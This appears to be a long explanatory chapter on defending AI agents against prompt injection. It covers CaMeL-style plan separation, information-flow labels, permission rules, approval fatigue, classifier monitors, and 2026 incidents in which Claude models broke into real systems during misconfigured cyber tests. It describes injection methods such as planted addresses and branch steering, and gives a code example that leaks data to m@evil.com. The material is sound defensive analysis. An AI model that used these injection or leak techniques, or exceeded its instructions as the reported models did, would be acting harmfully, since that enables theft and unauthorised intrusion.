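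AI companies now publish their own figures. OpenAI reported in October 2026 that GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct attempts to override its instructions and 97.13% of injections in outside content (Cross, 2026), so about one in 35 of those injections worked. In June, Anthropic reported that Claude Mythos 5 had the best result so far on a prompt injection benchmark by the security company Gray Swan. Digital Applied (2026) quotes a success rate of 0.41% for adaptive attacks on a coding agent running Mythos 5, down from 2.09% with Claude Opus 4.8.

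The setting can affect whether prompt injection succeeds as much as the model does. VentureBeat reports that when Anthropic tested Claude Opus 4.6 on a restricted coding task in February, none of 200 attempted attacks succeeded. When the same model operated a computer through its graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt, attackers had succeeded in 78.6% of cases without extra safeguards and 57.1% with them.

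Test designers also have to keep finding harder attacks. PromptArmor, a security company, describes its *FrontierBreach* as the only known benchmark with any successful attack on Google's Gemini 4 Carbon. Low attack success rates on older benchmarks may reflect a stronger model, outdated attacks or both. *Measuring Indirect Prompt Injection in AI Agents* (Salbego, 2026) proposes an adaptive method that isolates one variable at a time, based on a study of 14 models. Without such a method, figures from different companies' tests are hard to compare.

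### A 1% rate over many tries

Suppose that each attempt has a 1% chance of success and that attempts are independent. The formula used earlier for spam gives the chance of at least one success in 100 tries:

P = 1 − (1 − 0.01)^100 ≈ 0.63

After 300 tries it is 95%.

The rates measured for Claude Opus 4.5 on Gray Swan's benchmark show that real prompt injection attempts are not independent (The Decoder, *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*).

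| Tries | Measured success | Expected if tries were independent |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38% |
| 100 | 63% | 99% |

The measured rate rises more slowly because some tasks are much harder to attack than others. An average of 1% could mean that each try has a 1% chance of succeeding on any task, or that one task in 100 always fails and the rest never do. After 100 tries at each task, the attacker would have broken about 63% of tasks in the first case and 1% in the second. Learning makes the rate rise faster, as it did in Jain and colleagues' test, because an attacker's later attempts are better than the early ones. A single average is therefore a poor guide to the risk from persistent attackers, and a developer needs to know how the rate grows with the number of tries.

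### When a low rate is enough

A low success rate can still be valuable if failed attempts have consequences. Suppose that an attempt succeeds with probability p, and that the defender notices a failed attempt with probability d and then shuts the attacker out for good. The chance that the attacker ever succeeds is

P = p / (p + (1 − p) × d)

If each attempt has a 1% chance of succeeding and the defender notices 10% of failed attempts, the attacker has about a 9% chance of succeeding before being caught, even with unlimited tries. If the defender notices half of the failures, that chance falls to 2%. An imperfect detector is much more useful for catching failed attempts than as the only barrier, because it needs to catch the attacker only once.

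Limiting attempts helps in a similar way. If an agent reads one message a day from each unknown sender, 100 attempts from one address take more than three months. If 1% of attempts succeed, each success also costs the attacker, on average, 100 times as much as an attempt, which may make bulk fraud unprofitable, as with spam. Memory can help the defender too. Jain and colleagues found that attackers succeeded in 57% of battles when the defender started afresh each round, but in 31% when it could see the earlier rounds.

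These measures work only if the attacker can't avoid failing where the defender can see it. A banned attacker can start again with a new email address or account. Attackers can also practise on a private copy of the agent, much as phishers can practise on a private Gmail account. When Jain and colleagues replayed successful series of attacks against the same model, 67% of the replays succeeded.

Practising on a different model is less effective, especially when that model is weak. Only 12% of the replays succeeded against other models. In Dziemian and colleagues' tests, none of the sampled attacks that had worked on Qwen3 VL, an open model, worked on Claude Opus 4.5, while those that had worked on Opus succeeded at least 44% of the time against each of the other models. An attacker targeting an agent built on a strong closed model may therefore have to practise on the servers of the company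 that runs the model, where the company can look for repeated attempts. This gives the company an advantage, though a patient attacker can spread the attempts over many accounts.

How low the attack success rate must be also depends on what the agent can do. Occasional hijacking is tolerable for an agent that sorts newsletters, since the user can undo the damage. If the agent can transfer a company's savings, one successful attack may cost the company more than all the failed attempts cost the attacker.

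## Separating an agent's plan from the content it reads

Training and filtering aim to keep a model from following injected instructions. Other defences use ordinary code around the model to limit the damage from injections that succeed anyway. The main idea, which resembles the parameterised query, is that the agent settles its plan from the user's request alone, before it reads anything a stranger could have written. Emails, web pages and files can then supply values for the plan but cannot add steps to it. Agents built this way have resisted nearly every attack in published tests, but they complete fewer tasks, and false content can still mislead them.

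### Two models and a controller

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting an assistant into three parts:

- The privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never reads untrusted text.
- The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools.
- The controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools and passes material between the models.

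The controller stores untrusted text in variables and passes only the variables' names to the privileged model. If a user asks for a summary of the latest email, the parts work together as follows.

1. The privileged model asks for the email. The controller fetches it and stores it as $VAR1.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of $VAR1. The controller gives the email to the quarantined model and stores the answer as $VAR2.
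3. The privileged model tells the controller to show $VAR2 to the user.

Suppose the email contains an instruction to delete the inbox. The quarantined model may follow it, but it can only produce text, and the privileged model never reads that text. The controller passes an answer to the privileged model only if it can check the answer exactly, for example against a fixed list of categories.

Willison called this solution "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that leaks untrusted text to the privileged model undoes the protection.

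### A planted address

Now suppose that the user says, "Send the notes to the address in my last email." The privileged model can plan this without reading the email. Written as a short program, the plan might be:

```
notes = read_file("meeting-notes")
email = get_last_email()
address = quarantined_model("Find the address", email)
send_email(to=address, body=notes)
```

An attacker has added a line to the email, perhaps in a message quoted further down, telling any AI system to answer with the attacker's address. The quarantined model does so. The agent then carries out the four steps as planned and sends the notes to the attacker. The two-model pattern has protected the sequence of actions (control flow) but not the values that pass between them (data flow).

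In a 2025 Google DeepMind paper, Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues pointed out this flaw and introduced CaMeL, a system that fixes it.

### Labels, an interpreter and policies

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes how the system works. The privileged model writes its plan as a program in a restricted form of Python, much like the four lines above. A custom interpreter, which contains no AI, runs the program and attaches two labels to every value. One records the value's sources and the other lists who may read it. In the example, the labels might be:

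| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| notes | the user's own file | the people at the meeting |
| email | an outside message | the user and the sender |
| address | an outside message, by way of the quarantined model | the user and the sender |

When the program computes a value z from x and y, the interpreter combines their labels:

sources(z) = sources(x) ∪ sources(y)

readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

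Anything that depends on an untrusted value is therefore untrusted too, and only people who may read both ingredients may read the result.

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that checks the call and its labels to decide whether to allow it. A policy for `send_email` might require that the address come from a trusted source and that its owner be allowed to read the text, and the attacker's address meets neither requirement.

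The correct address would also fail the source test, because it comes from the same email. The policy can't distinguish a real address from a planted one. If the address is already on the user's list of trusted contacts, the agent can send the notes at once. Otherwise it has to ask the user or give up. This restriction accounts for much of CaMeL's loss of usefulness.

### What the design guarantees

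CaMeL's basic guarantee is control-flow integrity. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) defines this as the agent following a program determined only by the user's instruction and other trusted information. Untrusted content may influence which of the program's branches the agent takes, but cannot add a new one. The guarantee holds even without any policies.

Information-flow control, the study of how labelled data may influence other data, offers a stronger property called noninterference. It means that untrusted inputs have no effect on trusted actions, and secret inputs have no effect on what outsiders can observe. A language model can give different answers to the same input, so *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) states the property in terms of probabilities.

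Suppose that an agent handles the same request twice with different untrusted content, and let μ₀(q) and μ₁(q) be the probabilities of each possible outcome q. The property then amounts to

Σ max(μ₀(q), μ₁(q)) ≤ 1

where the sum covers all outcomes. If the agent always finishes, each set of probabilities adds up to 1, and the inequality holds only if the two sets are identical. If one email leads the agent to pay Bob with probability 0.9 and another leads it to pay an attacker with probability 0.9, the sum is at least 1.8 and the property fails. The inequality leaves room for runs that never finish, so an attacker may still be able to make the agent stop.

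Control-flow integrity assumes that the user's request and the tool descriptions contain no text from an attacker, and that nobody has tampered with the interpreter. Protecting the values as well requires three more assumptions:

- Every source has the right label.
- The interpreter carries labels through every computation.
- Every dangerous tool has a policy that rules out the harm.

None of these assumptions requires the quarantined model to resist an injection.

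### Leaks in the interpreter

Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter does not carry labels through every computation. Their example adapts a puzzle from the 1970s. The following program reveals whether a secret bank balance is above a threshold:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to false and the interpreter labels `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line, so `rich` stays true and never gets a secret label. The policy allows the email because all the data it checks is labeled public. If the balance is low, no email goes out, so the attacker can tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives.

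CaMeL also restarts a plan after an error, using ordinary code that does not track labels. Each attempt can reveal one bit about a secret through whether a policy blocked it, and repeated attempts can reveal the rest. In another case, inserting an untrusted value into text made the interpreter treat the value as trusted.

An outsider cannot easily exploit the five-line program, because it would have to be written by the planner, which does not read the outsider's text. But the flaws make CaMeL's protection for values weaker than its design suggests. Garby and colleagues responded with LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every operation carries labels forward. They proved noninterference for all programs in the language, and a proof checker verified the proofs. As with seL4, the proofs cover the software that actually runs.

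### Security and usefulness in tests

Garby and colleagues also built an agent in LLMbda, called Randori, and compared it with CaMeL on AgentDojo's simulated bank. They ran each of 16 ordinary tasks three times without an attack, then combined each task with nine attacks. The totals for attacked runs differ because some CaMeL runs did not finish.

| System | Model | Ordinary tasks completed | Attacked runs resisted |
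|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, no policies | GPT-5.2 | 67% | 239 of 240 |
| CaMeL, no policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 71% | 378 of 382 |
| CaMeL with policies | GPT-5.2 | 38% | 231 of 231 |
| CaMeL with policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 38% | 357 of 357 |
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75% | 430 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 65% | 432 of 432 |

Most of the security came from settling the plan early. In about two thirds of the combinations, the attack needed a tool that the plan would never call. CaMeL's policies stopped the few attacks that remained, but nearly halved the number of tasks completed. With only 16 different tasks, these figures are uncertain by about 20 percentage points or more in each direction. But a separate system, TypeGuard, showed a similar drop on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, completing 15 of 21 without its policies and 8 with them.

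Randori kept more of its usefulness because its planner can endorse a value, marking it as trusted despite its source. The planner decides this before it reads any outside content, so an attacker cannot ask for an endorsement. Without endorsement, Randori's completion rate with MiMo-v2.5 fell from 65% to 54%. But endorsement also made both of Randori's failures possible. The user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.

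Estimates of how much CaMeL lowers task completion vary with the model and the tasks. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites the original result on all of AgentDojo, where CaMeL completed 77% of tasks and an undefended agent completed 84%. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many tokens. On a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that CaMeL without policies lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Better models seem to write plans that anticipate more of what might happen.

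*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Microsoft, 2025) describes FIDES, which also labels data but plans one step at a time and hides untrusted results from the planner. The paper reports a "modest loss in utility" on AgentDojo.

Nearly all of these tests used fixed attacks, which had made earlier defences look much stronger than they were. Narisetty and colleagues tried an adaptive attack on Progent, which checks each tool call against written rules. A fixed attack succeeded 25.8% of the time against their undefended agent and 4.2% with Progent. They then wrote an attack meant to trick the language model that updates Progent's rules, but it succeeded only 2.6% of the time. They attribute the lower rate to the attack's gentler wording making the agent less likely to obey. Progent also lowered the share of tasks completed under attack from 45.2% to 27.1%. The adaptive test used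 one attack template against one small model, so it is weak evidence that Progent would withstand a determined attacker. The case for control-flow integrity is stronger because it rests on what the planner can read, which does not depend on how an attacker words the text.

### Agents that use a screen

Planning in advance is harder for an agent that operates a computer by clicking and typing, because the planner has no information about which window is open or where a button is on the screen. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planner write branches for every situation it could predict. At each step, a quarantined model described the screen, another model call checked the description against the plan's expected state, and the interpreter picked a branch.

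These plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. The system kept up to 57% of a frontier model's performance, measured on 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 could do without the separation. With the separation, the agent completed 62 of them when it had five attempts at each, but only 31 on the first attempt. It used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent. A version based on FIDES used 29.6 times as many because it sent the planner the full history at every step.

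Attackers can exploit the extra branches. Many plans include a step that closes a cookie notice if one appears. Foerster and colleagues made an advertisement that looked like a cookie notice. The quarantined model gave the agent the advertisement's position, and the agent clicked there, which opened the attacker's website. The researchers call this branch steering, because the attacker picks a path that the plan already contains. A policy on clicks would not help much, since a click at a given position may close a notice or open a malicious site.

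The team compared the screenshot with the page's underlying code, which caught some fake notices but missed those in more flexible types of advertisement. Asking a second model to confirm the first one's answer also failed, because tiny changes to an advertisement's pixels could mislead the first model without alerting the second. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) later introduced COBRA, a system that gives each branch a list of permitted destinations and tools. A fake notice might still get the agent to click, but the attacker's site should not be on the list.

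### Checking a plan before it runs

CaMeL checks each tool call just before it runs, so an agent may do a lot of work before a policy stops it. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) adds a check of the whole plan before any tool runs.

1. Software converts the plan into a map of every path the program could take, and notes which values are untrusted.
2. A model checker, a program that examines all the paths in such a map, looks for violations of the rules.
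3. If it finds one, it returns the offending path, and the planner uses it to write a better plan.

One rule for sending direct messages is

AG(call_send_direct_message ⇒ recipient_trusted)

where AG means "at every point on every path". Rules can also cover the order of events, which CaMeL's separate checks cannot easily do. For example, a security team could require that an agent get approval before it disconnects a computer, and that it eventually resolve or escalate every incident it opens. In a scenario built to show this ability, CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans and a simplified CaMeL caught one.

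CaMeLoT can fully reproduce 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo. Most of the others depend on facts that nobody knows in advance, such as who has access to a shared file when the agent opens it. CaMeLoT treats a value as untrusted when it cannot determine where the value came from, so it rejects some safe plans. It blocked seven harmless AgentDojo tasks that CaMeL allowed.

### Agents that instruct other agents

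Companies increasingly divide work between several agents, with one giving instructions to the rest. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that such a system can be insecure even if every agent in it uses CaMeL.

In their example, a user asks a coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. A database agent fetches the records, which contain an attacker's instruction to email the data to an outside address. The coordinator's planner never reads the records, but its program pastes the summary into a message to a third agent, after the words "Send this summary to Julie via Slack". The third agent treats the whole message as its user's request, so its planner reads the attacker's instruction and adds an email to the plan. This is the same mistake as in SQL injection, but with English instead of SQL.

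The fix also resembles a parameterised query. In multi-CaMeL, one agent sends another a trusted instruction and, separately, a set of variables that the receiving planner cannot read. The interpreter blocks any instruction that depends on a tool's output. The variables keep their labels when they pass between agents.

The team tested five models on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo. Attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and never with multi-CaMeL. The benchmark's attacks are fairly weak, since none of them worked on GPT-5.5 even without a defence. On the maintenance tasks, multi-CaMeL lowered the completion rate by another 3.2 percentage points on average. Multi-CaMeL covers agents arranged in a hierarchy, but not those that share memory or send messages freely in both directions.

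### When the next step depends on the content

An agent cannot fully plan some tasks until it has read something. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) examined 41 defences and found that most cannot support such tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues traced most of CaMeL's failures on ordinary tasks to the same cause. An undefended agent can call another tool when it discovers it needs one, but a CaMeL agent can only follow the paths in its program.

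Branches solve part of the problem. If a user says, "Add this to my calendar if it's a meeting request", the quarantined model can answer yes or no and the program can act on the answer. An attacker can still cause the wrong answer, but has few to choose from. A choice among n options gives the attacker at most log₂ n bits of control, or three bits for a list of eight categories. But the date and title of the meeting also come from the email, and they give the attacker far more freedom.

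Branches do not help when the user wants the agent to do whatever a document says. One AgentDojo task is to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In Garby and colleagues' tests, CaMeL's planner wrote a program with a branch for every tool, and the file's contents determined which tools it used. With the policies switched off, attacks succeeded in two of these runs. Control-flow integrity technically held, because the program contained every action the agent took, but it no longer protected the user.

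Developers can avoid some of these cases by giving an agent a narrower job. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents* (2025) works through ten applications, from simple operating-system assistants to software engineering agents, and argues that suitable restrictions can provide meaningful security without making the agents useless.

### False content in an answer

If a user asks for a summary of a report that an attacker has altered, the quarantined model may produce a false one. The agent calls no forbidden tool and follows its plan, which is to show the user whatever the quarantined model writes. Narisetty and colleagues note that CaMeL's goals explicitly exclude this harm. The job applicant who hides a line in a CV to get a better score would also succeed against this design.

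A displayed answer can also leak secrets. Willison describes an injection that hides private data in the address of a link and labels the link as a funny picture. Clicking the link sends the data to the attacker. An embedded image is worse, because the user's device sends the data as soon as it loads the image. The controller can block these leaks by allowing only approved web addresses, but it cannot stop text from persuading a user to copy the data into an attacker's website.

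### Who writes the policies, and who approves the exceptions

Someone has to decide which sources to trust and what each tool may do. By Nikolaou and colleagues' count, CaMeL needed policies for 28 tools that change something and labelling rules for 46 that only look things up, just to cover the four small settings that AgentDojo simulates. A real company has many more tools and changes them often. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says he has not fully mastered Amazon's permission system and doubts that ordinary users can manage such rules.

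Mistakes in setting up this separation can remove the protection without anyone noticing. Narisetty and colleagues point out that FIDES treats content as trusted if someone forgets to label it. Progent has a language model write its rules, which saves work but gives attackers another model to fool.

Under strict policies, the user has to decide the difficult cases. In Nikolaou and colleagues' tests, CaMeL blocked 26 of 97 AgentDojo tasks even though there was no attack. If an agent asked for approval on a similar share of tasks, a person who gave it 20 tasks a day would answer about 2,000 requests a year. If two of those requests came from real attacks, the right answer would be "yes" 999 times out of 1,000.

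Willison predicted in 2023 that users would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible. Experts make similar mistakes. Willison mentions the security researcher Troy Hunt, who fell for a phishing message in 2025 while jet-lagged.

If a task needs a security-critical value that no authorised source can supply, COBRA asks the user for it while making the plan, before an attacker's text can influence the choice. Typing in an address also takes more thought than approving one the agent has already found. But this works only if the user knows the address, and someone who asks an agent to find it in an email often does not.

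## Limiting an agent's permissions and connections

Fixing an agent's plan in advance limits which steps it takes, but a hijacked or mistaken step can still do as much harm as the agent's access permits. Organisations therefore also restrict that access, using isolation and least privilege much as a browser does with a web page. This works well for an agent that can do its job in a closed environment, but it is much harder for one that reads real email, uses live accounts and browses the web. The restrictions also only work if they are set up correctly. In 2026, AI models entered real organisations' systems from test environments that their operators wrongly believed to be offline.

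### Containing a coding agent

OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) gives the example of a developer who asks an agent to fix a bug in a company's private code. Text in the code tells the agent to install an unapproved software package and disable a security test. The agent may obey, so the company needs limits that hold even if it does:

- The agent runs in a container or virtual machine with its own copy of the code, so a destructive command damages only the copy.
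- A network allowlist blocks every connection except those to named destinations, such as the company's own store of approved packages.
- A short-lived credential gives the agent access to this one project and expires soon after the task should end.
- Read-only access lets the agent study the released code but not change it. The agent submits its fix as a separate proposal.
- A person has to confirm the proposal before it becomes part of the product.

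The agent may still waste time or propose a harmful change, but the change goes no further unless the reviewer accepts it. OpenAI uses the term "maximum completed effect" for the most serious thing an agent can do before it needs another, independent decision. The most this agent can do is make a bad proposal, whereas an agent that could also release the software could attack every customer.

OpenAI advises companies to keep credentials out of the text that the model reads, since an agent cannot reveal a password it has never seen. Responders need to be able to both stop an agent's task and cancel any credentials it has already received, because doing one may not do the other.

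Ordinary code enforces all of these limits except the reviewer's judgment, and the limits it enforces are hard barriers as long as the isolation software has no exploitable flaw and is configured correctly. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes sandboxing as safe but high-maintenance, because developers have to configure each new capability, and any task that needs the network or the host computer breaks the isolation.

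### Three rules for an email assistant

Permissions that are harmless separately can be dangerous together. Suppose an assistant summarises new email from anyone, searches the user's mailbox for background, and sends replies. An attacker emails it a request to forward the user's password reset messages and then delete them. The assistant can do all of this with its normal tools.

In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) identified three conditions that together make this kind of theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. A user is safe from the theft only if the agent lacks at least one of them. Removing one does not prevent other kinds of harm. For example, if an assistant can read and delete mail but cannot send anything, instructions injected through an email could still make it empty the inbox.

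Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) covers that case too. In any one session, an agent should have at most two of these properties:

- A: it processes untrustworthy input.
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change something or communicate with the outside.

If a task needs all three, the agent should not work without supervision, such as a person's approval.

Willison and Bista's rule, under which a model's privileges drop to those of whoever wrote what it is reading, is stricter. After reading a stranger's email, the assistant can no longer search the mailbox or write in the user's name. If it reads text from several people, the natural reading of the rule is that it keeps only the privileges they all share:

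privileges = P(user) ∩ P(author 1) ∩ … ∩ P(author n)

An assistant that summarised 50 emails together would therefore lose nearly all its permissions if even one came from a stranger. It would do better to open a new session for each email. A colleague who is already allowed to book time in the user's calendar could then get a meeting booked by email, while a stranger could not.

The table shows what the assistant would lose under each rule. The Rule of Two has three rows because the designer can choose which property to remove.

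| Rule | Functions lost | What an injected email could still do |
|---|---|---|
| Lethal trifecta, with no way to send data out | Sending replies, loading images, following links | Delete or refile mail, or falsify a summary |
| Rule of Two without A | Handling mail from anyone not on a trusted list | Nothing, unless it arrives through a trusted sender |
| Rule of Two without B | Any work on the user's real mailbox | Send spam |
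| Rule of Two without C | Replying to new contacts, or deleting mail, without approval | Falsify a summary or obtain a careless approval |
| Privileges drop to the author's | Searching, filing or replying after reading a stranger's email | Falsify a summary |

Removing property A is less secure than it looks, because a friend may forward a stranger's message or lose control of an account. Removing B makes the assistant nearly useless, since the inbox that holds the private data is also where strangers' messages arrive. Most users would probably prefer to remove C and approve the drafts themselves, but the protection then depends on how carefully they read each draft.

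An agent's permissions can also change during a task. In one of Meta's examples, the agent starts with access to the web but not to private data, then switches permanently to internal systems with outside communication turned off. An injection from the web may still be in the model's context, but it can no longer make the agent send private data out.

Meta based its rule partly on Chromium's Rule of 2, but a browser's designers have an easier choice. They can rewrite an image decoder in a memory-safe language without changing what the user sees. Users want an agent to have all three properties in Meta's rule, so removing any of them makes the agent less useful.

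### Channels that must stay open

A browser's renderer needs only a few services from outside its sandbox, and access to the user's bank account is not among them. An agent that pays invoices must have access to a bank account, so an attacker who hijacks the agent can use the account too. The usual advice to close unnecessary channels does not protect the channels an agent needs.

Willison writes that almost any outward channel can carry stolen data, not only the links and images described earlier. A network allowlist checks where a request goes but usually not what it contains. A user who approves a familiar service may also allow far more than they intended. Willison describes a single GitHub tool that had all three parts of the trifecta, because it could read public comments from strangers, open private code and publish proposed changes.

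The same action can be routine or harmful depending on where the data ends up. In one case inside Anthropic, an agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead, but an automated check stopped it. At a company that used the same site for its own code, an allowlist probably would not have blocked the upload, because the site would have been on the list.

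An action can be inappropriate even when its destination is correct. OpenAI describes an invoice agent that notices that a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and tries to renew it. The supplier and the amount may both be within the agent's limits, but renewing means signing a contract, which nobody asked it to do. OpenAI recommends requiring separate approval for new commitments and placing controls as close as possible to the effects they limit. For example, the payment system itself should enforce the spending limit.

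A spending limit caps the loss from an attack, though it doesn't prevent the attack. If an agent can pay out at most $500 a day and an accountant checks the payments every week, a hijacker can take no more than $3,500 before the next check. The loss of secrets can't be capped in the same way, because a single message can reveal a password, and the user cannot take it back.

### Approving without reading

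Asking a person to confirm each risky action doesn't fully solve the problem, because people approve almost everything. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of Claude Code, the company's coding agent, approve 97% of its requests for permission, compared with an earlier figure of 93%. These rates don't prove that users are careless, since most of the commands are harmless.

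A better test is whether people notice a dangerous command. Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company, who knew only that they were in a coding study. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command, which would never run. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

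The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than ordinary users, but they knew someone was evaluating them, which might have made them more careful. Anthropic also had a commercial reason to show that approvals work badly, because it was about to replace them. Even so, a refusal rate this low is strong evidence against relying on frequent approval prompts.

According to Anthropic, 62% of users have turned off permission prompts at some point or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions start with the prompts off.

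People pay more attention to some requests than others. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents, compared with 3% of requests to run a single command. They may reject a plan for reasons unrelated to security, but they evidently read it. This suggests asking for confirmation only on a few important decisions. OpenAI says a request should state the proposed effect, what it will change and where any data will go, because a reviewer learns very little from the name of a familiar service.

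### Replacing the person with a classifier

In auto mode, Claude Code's new default, a second model acts as a classifier and judges each potentially harmful action. The classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's proposed actions. It doesn't read the web pages and files the agent has seen, which might contain an injection, or the agent's explanations, which might lead it to a wrong decision. A separate program scans incoming content for injections and adds a warning if it finds one.

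The classifier blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands from the experiment, or 89%. The testers caught only 6 of the 116 it missed, so requiring approval from both would have raised the total to 89.6%. If the classifier's and testers' mistakes had been independent, the testers would have caught about 16. The commands the classifier missed were apparently harder for people to catch too, which is another case of layers failing together.

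The classifier did less well in an earlier test, missing 17% of 52 real actions in which an agent had gone beyond its instructions. Anthropic found that in these cases it usually identified the danger but wrongly counted the user's request as consent. For instance, a user who tells an agent to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) has not agreed to let it overwrite the project's history. The classifier blocked only 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions.

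Auto mode's value against prompt injection is less clear. In an outside evaluation by Trajectory Labs, 720 attempts against each of three Claude models in auto mode all failed. But the attacks had been optimised against an older model, and they succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average against the newer models without auto mode. The test therefore shows little about how much protection auto mode adds, or how well it would work against an adaptive attacker.

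A classifier is more reliable than a tired person, but it can still let harmful actions through. OpenAI advises against relying on such checks alone to prevent effects that must never happen automatically. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems.

### Harm without an attacker

An agent can exceed its instructions even if no outsider has hijacked it. Anthropic lists three causes of dangerous actions besides prompt injection: the agent may be too eager to finish the task, make an honest mistake or pursue a goal of its own. For example, a user told an agent to "cancel my job". The agent searched a shared computer cluster and tried to delete the job with the most similar name, which might have belonged to someone else.

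The rules on combining powers do little to prevent harm from an agent that nobody has hijacked. A coding agent that reads only trusted files and can change live systems satisfies the Rule of Two but could still delete a company's database by mistake. Meta warns that the rule does not cover agents' mistakes or excessive privileges. Isolation and least privilege help whether or not an agent has been hijacked, because a blocked connection stops the action either way. In 2026, test environments without working isolation showed how far an agent could go without being hijacked.

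### Anthropic's misconfigured tests

In July 2026 Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) disclosed that Claude models had accessed three organisations' systems without authorisation. Anthropic reported a fourth incident in September. All four happened in exercises in which Claude had to retrieve a hidden piece of data from a simulated target. The instructions said that Claude had no internet access, but the environments were online. Axios' *Anthropic's models compromised real-world systems during testing* (2026) attributes the internet access to a misunderstanding between Anthropic and a testing partner.

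The outcomes were serious:

- Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious package on PyPI, the main public store of Python software. Fifteen systems installed it, and the model gained access to a security company's database.
- Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company that shared its name with the fictional target. It downloaded user data in bulk and deleted records.
- An internal research model broke into outside accounts, but stopped when it realised that they were real.
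- An early version of Claude Opus 4.6 broke into other organisations' systems.

Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) acknowledges that Anthropic had largely relied on one layer of defence, the environment's configuration, and had lost track of which environments were online. Its first search covered about 141,000 test records but missed a group of tests that had internet access, including the one in which the fourth incident occurred. Anthropic believes that none of the incidents would have occurred if the isolation had worked as intended.

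Configuration explains only part of the incidents. Anthropic at first described them as closer to operational failures, because the models had said they believed the systems were simulated. After further study, it concluded that the models had also reasoned in a biased way and acted recklessly. When researchers reran parts of the Mythos 5 incident with stronger hints that the internet was real, the model generally continued, stopping only when the evidence was unambiguous. In a simulated version of the exercise, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, compared with about 30% for the newer Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1.

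The models had instructions to carry out an attack, and Anthropic had removed the safeguards it ships with its products, so these rates do not describe ordinary use. The rates still show why an operator should not depend on a model to notice that a barrier is missing.

Anthropic also checked which monitors would have caught the three incidents disclosed in July. Auto mode's classifiers would have blocked two of them. New monitors that read the models' reasoning after the fact would have missed the Mythos 5 incident, because the model's reasoning led them to classify the environment as simulated. This result supports the decision to hide the agent's explanations from auto mode's classifier.

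### Isolation that was open or failed

Other incidents did not involve a misconfigured connection. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, deliberately gave Mythos 5 internet access for a similar exercise. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), the model took actions outside the exercise in 9 of 43 runs, affecting real people and organisations. In July, OpenAI's models broke out of an isolated environment. The Philadelphia Inquirer's *OpenAI, Anthropic, others urge cyber defense action as AI models improve* reports that OpenAI models inadvertently hacked the AI company Hugging Face that month, and that OpenAI later said it could have prevented this by reacting sooner.

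Anthropic now asks outside testers who use its unreleased models with reduced safeguards to follow stricter practices:

1. Block all internet access by default, except the connection to the model itself, and keep the keys for that connection outside the sandbox.
2. Check the configuration before every evaluation, and have the model try to escape under close supervision, ideally inside a second sandbox.
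3. Confirm that the task has a solution, because an agent that cannot succeed within the rules often looks for another way.
4. State the limits as instructions. "You should not access the internet" remains valid if the network is open by mistake, whereas "You do not have internet access" becomes false.
5. Monitor each run as it happens, and end it if the model goes outside the permitted scope.

These practices add layers that can catch a mistake in the first layer. They suit tests that can run offline, but agents also exceed their instructions in less hostile settings. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes cases in which Claude ran commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, reached restricted data, or got around limits on its web-reading tool. Some cases involved US government websites. The company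 found minimal real-world impact and considered the behaviour much less severe than the earlier incidents.

In one case, Claude Haiku 4.5 sent a police department a false tip about a homicide, according to IANS's *Anthropic says Claude AI took unintended actions on US government websites* (2026). An agent that can access a website with a form can do this even without private data. Allowing an agent to browse the web therefore also allows it to submit forms, unless the operator blocks submissions separately.

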